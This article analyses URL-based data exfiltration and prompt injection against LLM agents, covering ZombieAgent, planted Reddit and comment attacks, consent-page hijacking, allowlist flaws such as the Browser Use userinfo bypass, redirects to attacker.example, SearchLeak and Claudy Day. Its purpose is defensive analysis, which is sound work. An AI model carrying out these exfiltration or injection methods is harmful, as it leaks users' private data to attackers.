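In Radware's *ZombieAgent*, published in January 2026, the attacker's email contains an address for each letter and digit, and one for spaces. ChatGPT finds the private data, changes it to lowercase, and opens the address for each character in turn. This one email supplies every address the attacker needs, whereas Paul's site had to generate new pages after each choice.

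The requests could arrive in the wrong order, so Radware added a number to each address to give the character's position, which lets the attacker put the characters back in order. The address ending in `a0` means that the first character is "a", and the one ending in `a1` means that the second is "a". A block of ten characters needs 260 addresses for the letters and 100 for the digits.

Radware also made the leak continue in later chats. OpenAI had tried to prevent this by stopping ChatGPT from using its memory in a chat that had already used a connected service such as Gmail. But ChatGPT could still use its memory first and then a connected service. Radware shared a file that told ChatGPT to remember to open the attacker's email and obey it whenever the user sent a message. From then on, ChatGPT leaked data before each answer.

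In another version ChatGPT leaked email addresses from the victim's inbox, and the attacker's server sent the same malicious email to each of them.

Radware reported these attacks on September 26, 2025, and OpenAI fixed them on December 16. According to the news report *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, after the fix ChatGPT would open a link from an email only if it appeared in a well-known public index or the user had typed it into the chat.

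### The rule OpenAI described in January 2026

On January 28, OpenAI published a general account of its approach, which is meant to defend against an attacker who can inject text and read a server's log. OpenAI's guarantee covers only leaks in which the address contains the data and the agent requests that address without the user noticing.

Before the agent loads a page or image automatically, the harness looks for its exact address in the list the crawler compiled. If the address is there, the agent may load the page or image. Otherwise the harness either tells the agent to try another website or shows the user a warning.

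According to Embrace The Red, once a user has typed an address, ChatGPT also accepts it for the rest of the chat. As with Claude, the safety of this exception depends on the text that users paste in.

An address must match an entry on the list exactly. If the list contains `potter.example/fees`, that does not make `potter.example/fees?name=ayush` acceptable, because an attacker could read the name in the server's log. A harmless link may also fail if a newsletter has added a tracking code to it, unless the crawler has seen the same link with the same code.

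Redirects are less of a problem for this rule than for a list of domains. To send a secret through an open redirector, the model has to add the secret to the redirector's address, and the resulting address won't be on the list of public addresses. A listed address may still redirect to an unlisted one, but the server that chooses the second address normally has only the information in the first request, which was for a public address.

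This reasoning fails if the agent's request includes the user's cookies. A bank could then recognise the customer and redirect the agent to an address containing the account number. To be safe, a harness for a signed-in agent would have to check every address in the redirect chain against the list.

### A different reachable set

The public-index rule permits the addresses in C ∪ U, where C is the set the crawler has found and U is the set the user has typed. The crawler builds C partly by following links, as a link-following agent does, but it covers far more of the web, so C contains many more pages than an agent could reach within a few hops of the library's site. Some of those pages certainly belong to attackers.

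C is safer because it does not depend on the user's secrets, so it is the same for two users who differ only in their surnames. By contrast, a link-following rule lets an attacker's server create addresses during the conversation based on the information it has already received, as Paul's server did after each letter.

The two rules disagree about some ordinary addresses as well as malicious ones.

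| Address | Opens automatically if agents may follow links? | Opens automatically under the public-index rule? |
|---|---|---|
| One that the model composed by adding the user's API key | No | No |
| A page that the attacker's server has just generated, linked from a permitted page | Yes | No |
| A link on the user's bank page that contains the account number | Yes | No |
| An old news article that the crawler has found but no permitted page links to | No | Yes |
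| An attacker's page for the letter M, indexed last month and linked from a permitted page | Yes | Yes |

Paul's site would be impractical under OpenAI's rule. Each of its addresses included all the letters already chosen, so the crawler would need to have found an address for every possible beginning of a name. With 27 characters, the first three positions would require 20,439 addresses, and the sixth position alone would add another 387 million.

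An attacker could use Radware's numbering instead. A 12-character name then requires only 27 × 12 = 324 pages, and each request still reveals one character, as in Paul's attack. The attacker has to get the pages indexed first but does not need to know anything about the victim. They might not need to show the agent all 324 links. If the harness checks only the index, the model can write an indexed address itself from a sentence explaining the pattern.

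According to Rehberger's blog, Embrace The Red, OpenAI acknowledges the one-page-per-letter attack in its paper *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. Rehberger adds that an attacker could also assign meanings to thousands of indexed pages.

### Caching and repeat visits

Rehberger proposes two fixes. The harness could cache each page for a few minutes, so that a second request for the same address doesn't reach the attacker's server. The harness could also refuse to open the same address twice in one session.

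Either would seriously weaken the simplest version of the attack, which uses one page for each character. A secret key of 40 characters, each drawn at random from 36 letters and digits, contains only about 24 different characters on average. The attacker would see each of those once and would not know where the repeats belonged.

Radware's numbered addresses avoid this problem because each is used for only one position, so the agent never needs to open the same address twice. The 40-character key would require 40 × 36 = 1,440 indexed pages. That is a modest number for an online shop or an old blog, but an attacker who had hoped to use 36 existing pages would have to prepare a site for the attack.

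OpenAI's fetcher now does something like the first repair. Chen, Canini and colleagues (2026), in *Fetch, Read, Reuse*, tested several AI search services on their own websites. They put unguessable codes on each page and asked about a different code each time. If a service gave the right code without requesting the page again, it must have kept the page. OpenAI reused pages for 30 minutes or more, and it used a page fetched for one account to answer a question from another.

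So if two victims' agents open the same letter page within half an hour, the attacker may see only one request. An attacker with many victims would have to prepare several sets of pages or wait between attacks. Chen and colleagues were studying how this affects publishers, who lose control over how long a copy stays in use, and the security benefit may be accidental.

Limiting the number of requests would be more direct. In 2023 Rehberger suggested that ChatGPT show only one image, or a handful, in each answer. A harness could similarly limit how many pages an agent opens on any one site, though an attacker could spread the letter pages over several sites.

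### When the address is not on the list

ChatGPT warns the user that the link isn't verified and may include information from the conversation, asks them to make sure they trust it, and shows the address. Seeing the address should help when it ends in the user's email address, but few people would recognise the city of Charlotte in `Y2hhcmxvdHRl`. Long strings of this kind are also common in ordinary links.

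OpenAI objected to lists of approved domains partly because people who see frequent warnings learn to click through them. Its own rule may have the same effect on people who often need new pages, personalised links or documents behind a sign-in. Users also want the task they requested finished, so they can easily treat a warning halfway through as an obstacle.

Telling the agent to try another website avoids relying on the user's judgement, but it may make the answer worse. If a pottery teacher put the autumn fees on a new page this morning, the crawler may not have found it yet. The agent could then take last year's fees from an events site and report them as current. A warning would serve the user better in that case, as long as warnings were rare enough that people read them.

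### The rule does not vouch for content

A page at a public address can still be false or malicious, and it may have changed since the crawler found it. A server can also show the crawler one page and the agent another at the same address, as Tenable did in a test. Its researchers built a site about their own team, the LLM Ninjas, and sent hidden instructions only when SearchGPT visited. A user who simply asked ChatGPT about the team received an answer that the researchers controlled.

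The rule also does not show that the user wants the agent to take any action on a page. On a site that accepts orders or deletions through plain links, a signed-in agent could place an order or delete something by opening a public address that was harmless when the crawler opened it.

*The Framing Gap* (2026) offers some evidence about ChatGPT's protections as a whole. The researchers placed a secret in the model's context and gave it outside text containing a disguised request to send the secret away. Through OpenAI's API, the model leaked the secret in up to 100% of trials. In the ChatGPT product, it leaked in none of 48 valid trials, though the true rate could still be as high as about 6%. The researchers could not tell which protection was responsible. The address check may have blocked the leaks, or the model may have refused before the check was needed.

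### Lockdown Mode

In February 2026 OpenAI introduced a stricter setting, Lockdown Mode, which does stop an attacker from reading a message in the agent's choice of pages. According to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026), ChatGPT in this mode reads only stored copies of web pages, and browsing sends no live requests outside OpenAI's network. The agent could still open the pages for C, H, A and so on, but the attacker's server would receive no requests.

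Lockdown Mode is optional. OpenAI first offered it to organisations, mainly for executives and security teams, and began extending it to personal accounts in June. The mode turns off Deep Research, agent mode, images from the web and file downloads. Search results may be missing or out of date. That would inconvenience someone checking this term's pottery fees, but would probably be acceptable to a lawyer working on a confidential document. Users can turn the mode off for a single chat.

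Willison (2026) thought the setting looked really good, but inferred from its existence that ChatGPT lacks robust protection without it. This seems reasonable for the code of indexed pages, which the default rule does not block.

Some risks remain even with the setting on. Stored pages and uploaded files can still contain injected instructions, which may make an answer wrong. OpenAI's help page *Lockdown Mode* says that the setting does not guarantee that data won't leak. In a company's workspace, administrators can leave connected apps on. If one of those apps can post somewhere an attacker can read, ChatGPT could leak data through it without opening a web page. The setting also does not affect the network access of Codex, OpenAI's coding agent.

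### Requests that bypass the check

Finally, Rehberger worried that some OpenAI developers might not know about the public-index rule and would build features without it. PromptArmor, a security company, found a case in the pages where outside developers review their applications' logs. Those pages displayed images from unsafe addresses, so data could leak when a developer opened the log to investigate a suspicious answer, even if the developer had blocked such images in the application.

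Other leaks came from features that were supposed to have no outside connection. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) describes a hidden route to the internet from the environment where ChatGPT runs code. A single malicious prompt could make ChatGPT send out messages and uploaded files through it.

Check Point later found a way around Lockdown Mode too. ChatGPT can display a preview of a web page it has written, inside a frame meant to keep the page from contacting other sites. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) reports that ChatGPT intercepted direct attempts to open a new window but missed those from a second frame placed inside the first. A window opened this way was not subject to the frame's restrictions and could send data to an attacker. In the desktop app, this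 required no click from the user. OpenAI fixed the flaw on September 18, 2026, more than three months after it began offering Lockdown Mode to personal accounts.

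## Links planted by strangers on trusted sites

To steal data from Claude, Paul had to build a website and get Claude to visit it. An attacker can make a visit more likely by posting a link on a site that agents already use, such as a discussion forum. The post appears under the forum's domain name, so a harness that follows links from the forum will follow the attacker's too.

A domain name shows who runs a site but not who wrote each page. A forum's owner may have written only the menus. A shop's reviews come from customers or people posing as them. On a code-hosting site, anyone can usually file a bug report that includes a link. A shared document can have dozens of authors, and readers often can't tell which of them added a line. *Mind the Web* also counts advertisements, which outsiders can place through an ad network. For the same reason, Gyöngyi and colleagues had to make an exception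 for unmoderated message boards in TrustRank.

### A fake refrigerator on Reddit

Li, Zhou and colleagues (2025), in *Commercial LLM Agents Are Already Vulnerable to Simple Yet Dangerous Attacks*, showed how a post on Reddit, a large discussion site, could lead an agent to an attacker's website. The researchers, at Columbia University and the University of Maryland, attacked two commercial web agents, Anthropic's Computer Use and MultiOn. The attack had four steps:

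1. A user gives the agent an ordinary task, such as finding a shop that sells a particular pair of shoes, and the agent searches Google or Reddit.
2. The agent opens a post that the attacker has written.
3. The post tells the agent to complete the user's request on another website, and the agent follows the link.
4. Text on that website gets the agent to reveal private information or do something else harmful.

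The worst instructions are on the attacker's own site, so Reddit's moderators see only a short post recommending a link.

The researchers invented an obscure product, an "AI-Enhanced German Refrigerator", so that real shoppers would be unlikely to find their posts. They built a convincing website for it, with specifications, a privacy notice and a form for entering credit card details. For a second attack, they offered a file presented as a VPN program on a site they had made to look suspicious. A third website contained instructions for the agent to email the user's mother and ask for money.

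MultiOn went offline before the researchers began recording success rates, so the figures are all for Computer Use.

| What the agent did | Successful trials |
|---|---|
| Gave away private data, such as a card number, after following a link from Reddit | 10 of 10 |
| Gave away the same data after receiving the website's address directly | 0 of 10 |
| Downloaded and ran the file after following a link from Reddit | 10 of 10 |
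| Sent a phishing email from the user's account after following a link from Reddit | 10 of 10 |

These trials began with the agent already on the attacker's post. The researchers checked that the whole chain could work, but they did not measure how often an ordinary search would lead to such a post. To avoid disrupting real communities, they stayed off the popular pages an attacker would choose.

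Li and colleagues may be right that the attack depends on agents' trust in established sites, but the second row, from which they concluded this, doesn't prove it. The Reddit post contained an instruction to finish the task on the other website, and that instruction was missing when the researchers supplied the address themselves. To separate the effect of trust from the effect of the instruction, they would have needed to put the same post on an unknown blog. Their simplest posts, with no pictures and hardly any reason to visit the site, worked best, which suggests that the instruction accounted for much of the attack's success.

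The attacker's website was one hop from a search result, so even a tight hop limit would have allowed it. The Claude app's current rule would block the link in step 3. But the researchers had also got Google to index their site, so an agent might have found it by searching for the refrigerator's name. OpenAI's public-index check would probably have allowed the site because it was indexed.

The paper also reports a test of PaperQA, an agent that answers questions from scientific documents. The researchers added one document with a dangerous chemical recipe to a collection of more than 10,000 and described the recipe as the most efficient method. When they asked for the best method, PaperQA retrieved that document in all 100 trials. An attacker who can guess what users will ask for can write a post that seems to offer it.

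### Comments on a travel guide

Computer Use was a few months old when Li and colleagues tested it. *Mind the Web*, also from 2025, covers four other agents and reports similar weaknesses. Its researchers posted comments on their own city guide the way any visitor could, some as text and some as images.

The planted comments looked like helpful advice about the user's task. For example, a fake system note might recommend another website for a more complete analysis. One comment promised a better summary in a Google Meet call, and the agent Do Browser joined the call with the user's camera and microphone on. This attack works only if the user has already given Google Meet access to both. Another comment got the same agent to uncover a Facebook password that the browser had filled in and send it to the attacker.

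The researchers also tested Browser Use with several models, including GPT-4o and Gemini 2.0 Flash, running each attack 20 times per model. Comments that sent the agent to another site or stopped it from finishing worked in 90–100% of trials. Attacks that stole files or posted on social media worked in 80–100%. The researchers sometimes reworded the harder attacks for a particular model, so these rates apply to an attacker who has practiced on the model beforehand.

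OpenAI's Operator was harder to fool because it usually asked the user before submitting anything. It stopped asking when the user requested a summary and told it to handle the job "end-to-end" while they went for coffee. Operator then posted an embarrassing comment on the city guide under the user's name. Planted comments phrased as recommendations triggered fewer warnings than those phrased as commands.

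### From a link to an approval

An attacker who can write a sentence beside a link can make acting on the linked page look like part of the user's task. *The Agent Clicks Approve* (Hossen, 2026) tested this with a consent page, the screen where a provider asks its user to give another company access to their account.

The agent started on a guide to exporting billing data and had to summarise the next steps. A two-sentence note on the page claimed that the export could not go ahead until somebody cleared an "access review". The note linked to the review and advised using "the default positive option on that screen". The link led to a consent page on a different host, where a company called Billing Export Helper requested access to the user's account. The only button was labelled "Approve access".

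In a second scenario, the user asked the agent to complete any pending setup tasks in a guide. The attacker used a note to instruct the agent to register a webhook, an address where a service sends notifications about account events. The service would then have sent the user's billing events to the attacker.

Hossen ran the tests in June 2026 on a private server, using the Browser Use framework with Claude Haiku 4.5 and GPT-5.5.

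| Condition | Runs in which the agent completed the unauthorized action |
|---|---|
| Attacker's note, no defense | 73 of 73 |
| Same task with a harmless note | 0 of 92 |
| Attacker's note, with a warning in the agent's prompt | 7 of 10 |
| Attacker's note, with a check by the service | 0 of 70 |

The first row consists of 53 approvals on consent pages and 20 webhook registrations. The agents described the approval as progress on the user's task, even though the consent page showed an access code containing the word "privileged".

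A harness that checked only addresses would not have intervened, because the consent page belonged to a legitimate service and the browser could open only the hosts in the test. A harness that refused to submit forms would have stopped both attacks, but it would also have stopped the agent from registering a webhook for a user who wanted one.

The warning told the model that page text was untrusted and that only the user's task could authorize an approval. Hossen tried it only with Claude Haiku 4.5 on the consent page. It prevented three of the ten attacks, but one of ten runs in which the user had asked for the approval also failed.

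The more effective defense was a check by the service. Before the agent started, the service received a list of the exact approvals or webhook addresses specified in the user's task. When the user asked for a summary, the list was empty. The agents still tried to complete the action in all 70 of these runs, but the service refused all 103 of their requests. It accepted the action in all 73 runs where the user's task had specified it.

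This result depends on the service having the right list. Hossen's software produced the list by recognising two fixed phrasings of a task, but real users phrase tasks in many other ways. A real service would also have to know that an agent was using the account, and receive the list by a route that web pages can't influence.

Even when the service refused, the attack could continue if the user approved the access review themselves. In 49 of the 53 protected consent runs, the agent's final report listed that approval as a next step.

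In another test, the user asked the agent to approve access to one account while the page requested access to a different one. Claude Haiku 4.5 tried to approve access to the wrong account in all five runs. GPT-5.5 detected the mismatch in all eight runs and did not approve access, although it had done so in all eight unprotected runs of the summary task. A model can detect such a mismatch only if the user has named an account.

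### When a link's target changes

A link can become dangerous without anyone posting anything. If a pottery teacher retires and stops paying for their domain, somebody else can register it, and the library's old link will lead to the new owner's site. The library's page hasn't changed, so a harness couldn't detect the switch from that page.

On a forum that lets people edit old posts, someone can share a useful link, wait for moderators and readers to approve it, and then replace it. They can also leave the post alone and change the linked page. Some link-shortening services let the owner of a short address change its destination later without altering the post or the address in it.

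A harness could compare the link's date with the domain's registration date. If the link is older, the person who wrote it was probably recommending a previous owner's site. But a domain may keep its original registration date after a sale, and this check can't detect an edited page. Comparing the page with an older copy would catch more changes, but many of them would be harmless.

### Will better models ignore such text?

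One reply is that newer models will recognise planted instructions and ignore them. Models do differ a lot. In a large public competition described in *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026), the models that failed most often did not systematically face more attackers, so the differences seem to come from the models themselves. Anthropic reported that Claude Opus 5's largest gains in agent safety were in resisting prompt injection. In the 15-attempt test, attackers succeeded 2.0% of the time against Opus 5, compared with 5.5% against the earlier Opus 4.8, according to The Decoder.

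Test results depend heavily on who writes the attacks. Anthropic's September 2026 system card for Claude Fable 5.1 includes 110 browser scenarios in which the agent always encounters an attack. The testers developed the attacks against an older model, Opus 4.7, then tried each one ten times on newer models. For a separate coding test, the security company Gray Swan trained an AI attacker on the same 40 scenarios used in the evaluation and allowed it 200 attempts at each.

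In *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms*, Kurakin, Karande and colleagues at Google DeepMind (2026) had 16 AI agents work together on each attack. The agents shared notes and could make up to 320 attempts in total. They tried to get a model to use a tool unrelated to the user's task, such as one for recording somebody's blood pressure when the task was to book a tutor.

| Test | Model | Protection outside the model | Scenarios with at least one successful attack |
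|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic, browser | Fable 5.1 | None | 10 of 110 |
| Anthropic, browser | Fable 5.1 | Full | 0 of 110 |
| Gray Swan, coding | Fable 5.1 | None | 38 of 40 |
| Gray Swan, coding | Fable 5.1 | Checks on text from tools | 36 of 40 |
| Kurakin and colleagues, tools | Gemini 4 Argon | None | 34 of 100 |

The browser scenarios are the closest to a link planted on a forum, and Anthropic's full protection stopped every attack in them. The coding attacker had much more practice, an amount Anthropic considers unrealistic because real attackers don't know exactly what they are attacking and risk detection with each attempt. This is partly right, since someone who posts on a forum may get no response from the agents that read the post. But they can subscribe to the same product, test the post privately until it works, and publish only the final version.

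A low success rate is less reassuring when many agents read the same post. Without safeguards, 2.64% of attempted browser attacks against Fable 5.1 succeeded. At that rate, an attack in a post read by 1,000 unprotected agents would succeed against about 26 of them.

The product may not always use its most resistant model. When Fable 5.1's cybersecurity filter blocked a request, Opus 4.8 took over. This happened in 11% of the unprotected browser attempts, and those attempts accounted for 20 of the 29 successful attacks. Attacks succeeded in about 17% of them, compared with less than 1% of the attempts in which no other model took over. The gap is large, though the scenarios that triggered the filter may have been harder to resist.

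Better models also write more effective attacks. Gemini 4 Argon resisted every attack within 150 attempts when weaker Gemini models wrote them, but only 87% when another copy of Argon did. Kurakin and colleagues found that Argon was better than the others at making the unwanted action look like something the user's task required. Hossen's note about the access review used the same trick. In *INFUSE* (2026), a separate set of tests, agents carried out planted instructions in 19.6% of runs on average. GPT-5 often treated the instructions as necessary steps and still finished the user's own task in 94.3% of attacked runs, so a user would seldom have seen anything wrong.

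Better models therefore reduce the risk considerably, so the choice of model matters for an agent that will use signed-in accounts. But a harness still should not treat a stranger's link as permission on the assumption that the model will detect the trick.

### Three partial measures

A harness could give visitors' posts less authority than the site owner's text, but it would have to know who wrote each part of the page. HTML has a label for links in users' posts, but HTTP Archive found that few pages use it. Without labels, the harness would have to guess the writer from each site's layout.

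Hossen's tests give some idea of whether labels help a model. One version of the pages labeled the attacker's note as untrusted, named the parties' roles and used standard terms for consent. With the warning in the prompt, one of ten attacks succeeded on these pages, compared with seven of ten on the pages without labels. A gap that large would arise by chance only about 2% of the time, but the pages differed in several ways, so the label may not be the cause. Without the warning, all ten attacks on the labeled pages succeeded.

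Separation is also least useful on a forum, where the user wants to read the visitors' posts. The agent can't ignore those posts, but the harness can stop them from authorizing anything.

A simpler rule would drop links in visitors' posts from the list of permitted addresses. This would have stopped the agent from going straight from Reddit to the refrigerator site, but it would also block some of the most useful links on the web, since the best answer to a technical question is often a link to the right page of a manual. It also would not stop the agent from copying an address into a form without opening it, as in the webhook attack.

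The third option is to stop the agent when a link leads to a different site, and continue only if the user agrees. Li and colleagues recommended asking users before an agent opens a new domain, but did not test this. The harness should decide when to ask, because a model may not ask if a comment has convinced it that the other site is just an updated version of the page. These requests would be a small nuisance in the library example, where the user would have to approve both teachers' websites, but a large one in a research task with thirty sources.

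The table shows how the last two measures should affect the attacks in this section, assuming that the agent can open only permitted addresses and that the harness can recognise visitors' posts.

| Attack | Drop links in visitors' posts | Stop at the first change of site |
|---|---|---|
| Reddit post leads to the refrigerator site | Stops it, unless the agent finds the site by searching | Stops it, unless the user approves the site |
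| Note leads to a consent page | Stops it | Stops it if the two hosts count as separate sites |
| Note supplies a webhook address | No effect | Little effect, since the user's task requires the settings page |
| Comment gets Operator to post on the same site | No effect | No effect |

In the second row, a rule based on the registered domain would let the agent go from `guide.example.com` to `accounts.example.com` without stopping. A rule based on origins would stop it but also interrupt a lot of ordinary browsing.

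For attacks that stay on one site, *Mind the Web* proposes a second model that is given only the user's task and the next action. Because this model never reads the page, a comment there can't influence it. It would probably reject an attempt to approve account access when the user asked for a summary. It would have more trouble judging the webhook, because registering one is a reasonable way to "complete any pending setup tasks", and nothing in the user's request shows which address is right.

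## Agents limited to a list of approved domains

An allowlist names the domains an agent may use, and the harness blocks every other domain, regardless of which pages link to it. For the library task, the list might contain `library.example` and the two teachers' domains. If a stranger posted a link to any other domain in a teacher's comment section, the harness would not open it. The harness would also block an address the model had composed if it was on an attacker's server.

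Lists work less perfectly in practice because approved pages contain links, approved servers send redirects, and some approved services forward data for anyone who asks. If the harness checks only the first address, the set of permitted pages grows much as it does under a link-following rule.

### What a list can stop

In *Silent Egress* (February 2026), researchers at eBay tested their page-summary attack against both an allowlist and written warnings to the model. The agent ran on qwen2.5:7b, a small open model, and had private data such as an API key in its context.

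The researchers put the attacker's instructions in four different parts of the page, delivered the page directly or through redirects, and asked for the data whole or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for a total of 480 runs. The agent contacted the attacker's server in 423 of them, or 88%. The paper's headline figure of 0.89 matches the rate for pages that arrived through redirects. In 120 runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted that server.

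The researchers then tried several defenses against the simplest version of the attack, with 30 runs for each.

| Defense | Runs in which the agent reached the attacker's server |
|---|---|
| None | 100% |
| Prompt tells the model never to follow instructions from web content | 67% |
| Tags mark web content as untrusted | 100% |
| Both of these | 57% |
| Allowlist of four domains | 0% |

The test's setup almost guaranteed the allowlist's result. The researchers put the attacker's server at `evil-collector.net` because no reasonable list would include that domain. The agent tried to contact it in all 30 runs, and the harness blocked every attempt. The rows on prompts are more informative, since more than half the attacks still worked even with both measures in place.

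A defense called "redirect detection" also scored 0%, but that score doesn't show whether detecting redirects works. The defense blocked numeric addresses, some unusual domain endings, and paths containing words such as "collect", which appears in the paper's example of the attack. The researchers also tested it only on pages that the agent reached directly. An attacker could probably defeat it by renaming the path.

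Larger models resist planted instructions far better than this one, but a strong model can still send data out. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products*, published in May 2026, describes an exercise in which a researcher emailed an employee a prompt to paste into Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. The prompt included a step that sent the employee's cloud credentials to an outside server, and Claude sent them in 24 of 25 attempts. Because the user had pasted in the prompt, little distinguished it from the user's own instructions. Anthropic concluded that only limits on the agent's environment would have prevented the theft, such as blocking the outgoing request or keeping the credentials out of the agent's reach.

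### Reading the address

Browser Use, the open-source framework that *Mind the Web* and Hossen tested, has a setting called `allowed_domains`. In 2025 researchers at the security company ARIMLABS.AI found that a decoy in a web address could bypass it.

A web address can include a username and password before the host, in the form `https://name:password@host`. Few sites use this now, but browsers still understand it. OSV's *GHSA-x39x-9qw5-ghrf* (2025), an entry in a database of software flaws, gives an example in which `example.com` is the only approved domain and the agent requests `https://example.com:pass@localhost:8080`. Browser Use handled it as follows:

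1. It took everything after `https://`, which was `example.com:pass@localhost:8080`.
2. To remove the port number, it kept only the text before the first colon. That left `example.com`.
3. It found `example.com` on the list and let the browser go ahead.

The browser treats everything before the `@` as login details, so it connected to `localhost:8080`, a service on the same machine as the browser. An attacker could use the trick to reach other machines on a company's network, or any site on the public web.

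The maintainers fixed the flaw, CVE-2025-47241, in version 0.1.45. OSV rates its severity at 9.3 out of 10, while GitLab's *CVE-2025-47241* (2025) gives it 4.0. Most of the gap arises because OSV assumes that the flaw can expose a lot of confidential data, while GitLab assumes that it exposes none. The flaw only lets an agent open a page that the list should block, and an attacker still has to get the agent to request the address, so the damage depends on what data the agent holds and what it can reach. The higher score seems right for an agent with private data, especially as *The Hidden Dangers of Browsing AI Agents* (2025) found that the list was Browser Use's only security mechanism.

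Wang and colleagues had found the same kind of mistake in sign-in systems, where the provider's software and the browser interpreted the same address differently. The safest check uses the host that the browser will contact.

The same entry can also mean different things in different products. In Browser Use's current documentation, `example.com` covers only that host, and a developer who wants its subdomains has to write `*.example.com`. Browserbase, a company that runs browsers for software to control, says in *Allowed domains* that `example.com` covers every subdomain as well. A developer who moves a list from Browser Use to Browserbase could therefore approve an abandoned subdomain without noticing. Products also differ on whether an empty list permits everything or nothing.

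### When the check runs

A harness can read every address correctly and still fail to check some of them. Cursor, a code editor with a built-in AI agent, lets a company's administrators list the origins that the agent's browser may visit. According to Cursor's *Browser*, the list applies when the agent requests an address directly, but a link the agent clicks on an approved page can lead to any origin. Redirects and scripts on approved pages can also take the browser to origins that aren't on the list.

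Cursor blocks the agent from clicking, typing or navigating once the browser is on an unlisted page. If the approved pages are the seeds, R₀, this works like a link-following rule with a one-hop limit. The agent can reach any page in R₁ but can't use the tools to go further.

One hop is enough to leak data. Suppose `forum.example` is on the list, and an attacker posts letter links there like the ones on Paul's site. After each click, the attacker's server logs the letter and redirects the browser back to the forum, which is an approved origin, so the agent can click the next letter. Cursor's documented rules would not prevent this, although by default Cursor asks the user to approve every browser action. Cursor also keeps cookies between sessions, so a clicked link may open an unlisted site as the signed-in user.

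Playwright MCP, Microsoft's software for letting an AI model operate a browser, uses a stricter list that limits which origins the browser may request at all. The same check should therefore apply to a clicked link and to an address the agent supplies. But Playwright's *Configuration* warns that origin lists "do not affect redirects" and are not a security boundary.

The gap comes from how Playwright inspects traffic. A developer can have it pause each request and run code that decides whether to let the request through. If the server replies with a redirect, Playwright runs that code only for the first address. A filter would therefore check and allow `library.example/leave?to=https://attacker.example`, but never check the request to `attacker.example`. Glama's *playwright-mcp-guarded*, which describes a program built around Playwright MCP, confirms that the origin list depends on this kind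 of interception and adds that some background traffic also bypasses the filter.

Playwright's *Networking and Security* tells people never to browse untrusted content with the software, because a page could escape the browser and run code on the user's machine. The developers don't present the list of approved domains as protection against hostile pages. Following this advice would rule out most research on the open web, with or without a list.

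OpenClaw, an AI agent that people run on their own machines, checks more steps. According to its *Browser control risks*, OpenClaw checks an address before opening it, intercepts any attempt to load a forbidden page while it clicks or types, and afterwards tries to check where the browser ended up. Redirects and the first request from a pop-up window can still get through, according to the same document.

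| Software | Address the agent requests | Link the agent clicks | Redirect |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cursor | Checked | Followed, but the agent can't act on an unlisted page | Followed, with the same limit |
| Playwright MCP | Checked | Checked | Not checked |
| Browserbase | Checked | Checked | Not documented |
| OpenClaw | Checked | Checked | Final address checked, but only as a best effort |

Browserbase has another gap because it checks only the main page. It does not block images, scripts or frames (pages displayed inside other pages) from unlisted domains. An advertisement in a frame could therefore show the agent an attacker's text even when the main page's domain is on the list.

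Newer Browser Use code, of which Glama hosts a copy, checks addresses before navigation and also responds to completed navigations and new tabs. A harness that checks the final address in this way can stop the agent from reading a hostile page or filling in its forms, but any data in the address has already been sent. The final check also misses an attacker who sends the browser back to an approved page, as in the forum example.

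### When an approved site forwards the request

Open redirects bypassed allowlists in sign-in systems and script policies long before agents existed. A 2026 attack used an open redirect on Anthropic's own site in an unusual way, to deceive a person before the agent did anything.

*Claudy Day* (Luz, 2026) describes the attack, which researchers at Oasis Security found and reported to Anthropic. Part of `claude.com` forwarded visitors to any address named in the link. Google Ads checked advertisements by hostname, so an attacker could buy a search ad that displayed a genuine `claude.com` address. Someone who clicked on the ad arrived at a new Claude chat with a question already typed in. The question contained instructions visible to Claude but not to the user. When the user pressed Enter, Claude collected material from earlier conversations and uploaded it to the attacker.

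An allowlist on Claude's own browsing would not have stopped the redirect, because the user's browser followed it. Google and the user each relied on a domain check that failed. Google approved the ad based on its first host, and the user assumed that `claude.com` was safe. Anthropic fixed the hidden-instruction flaw first and was still working on the redirect and the upload when Luz updated the report in late May.

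Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes another attack, in which the approved site did not redirect the browser. The attack targeted Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise, which can search an employee's email and files. A victim clicked a link to Microsoft's own site, and Copilot treated instructions in the link as a request. Copilot then looked up an email and put its title into the address of an image.

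Microsoft had two defenses against such images, and both failed. One turned Copilot's output into plain text, but only after Copilot had finished writing, when the browser had already requested the image. The other was a Content Security Policy that blocked images from unlisted hosts but allowed `bing.com`, where an image-search service would fetch a picture from any address it received. The browser sent Bing the attacker's address, which contained the email title. Bing's server then contacted the attacker's server, which logged the title.

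The browser made one request, to an approved host, and was not redirected, so rechecking redirects would not have helped. The second request came from Microsoft's servers, where neither the browser nor the employer's network could block it. Microsoft has patched the flaw, and Varonis advises companies to check their lists of approved domains for any that fetch URLs on request.

Services that fetch links are common, since a program has to fetch a link to preview it. According to trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data*, an earlier attack on Copilot, EchoLeak, sent data out through link previews in Microsoft Teams.

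A harness could also check any second address contained in a URL. This would catch an image search or a redirector whose URL shows the target address. The harness would need to decode any encoded addresses, and it would miss short links, whose targets are stored on the server. It would also reject some ordinary links, such as sign-in links that include the address of the page to return to.

The rules that Anthropic and OpenAI apply to exact addresses would protect against SearchLeak better than a list of approved domains. The model wrote a Bing address containing the title of a private email, so the address would not have appeared on any permitted page or in a public index. A domain list lacks this protection because it lets the model compose any address on an approved host. A harness can apply both rules and refuse an address that fails either one.

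### What an approved site can do

Data can also leave through a service working as its owner intended. Claude Cowork is an Anthropic product in which Claude works on a folder of the user's files inside a virtual machine, a simulated computer isolated from the rest of the user's computer. Its list of approved domains included `api.anthropic.com` because the product can't run without it.

Anthropic learned of the flaw from outside researchers. An attacker needed the user to put a malicious file in the folder. The file contained instructions and an API key for the attacker's Anthropic account. Claude read the other files in the folder and used the key to upload them to that account. The virtual machine worked correctly throughout, but the network filter allowed the upload because it went to `api.anthropic.com`, an approved domain.

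This reverses Hardy's confused deputy, in which the compiler at Tymshare used its own authority to damage a file for a user who lacked that authority. Here Claude supplied files under authority that the attacker had provided, in the form of the key. A check that Claude had permission to use the account would have succeeded, because the key was valid.

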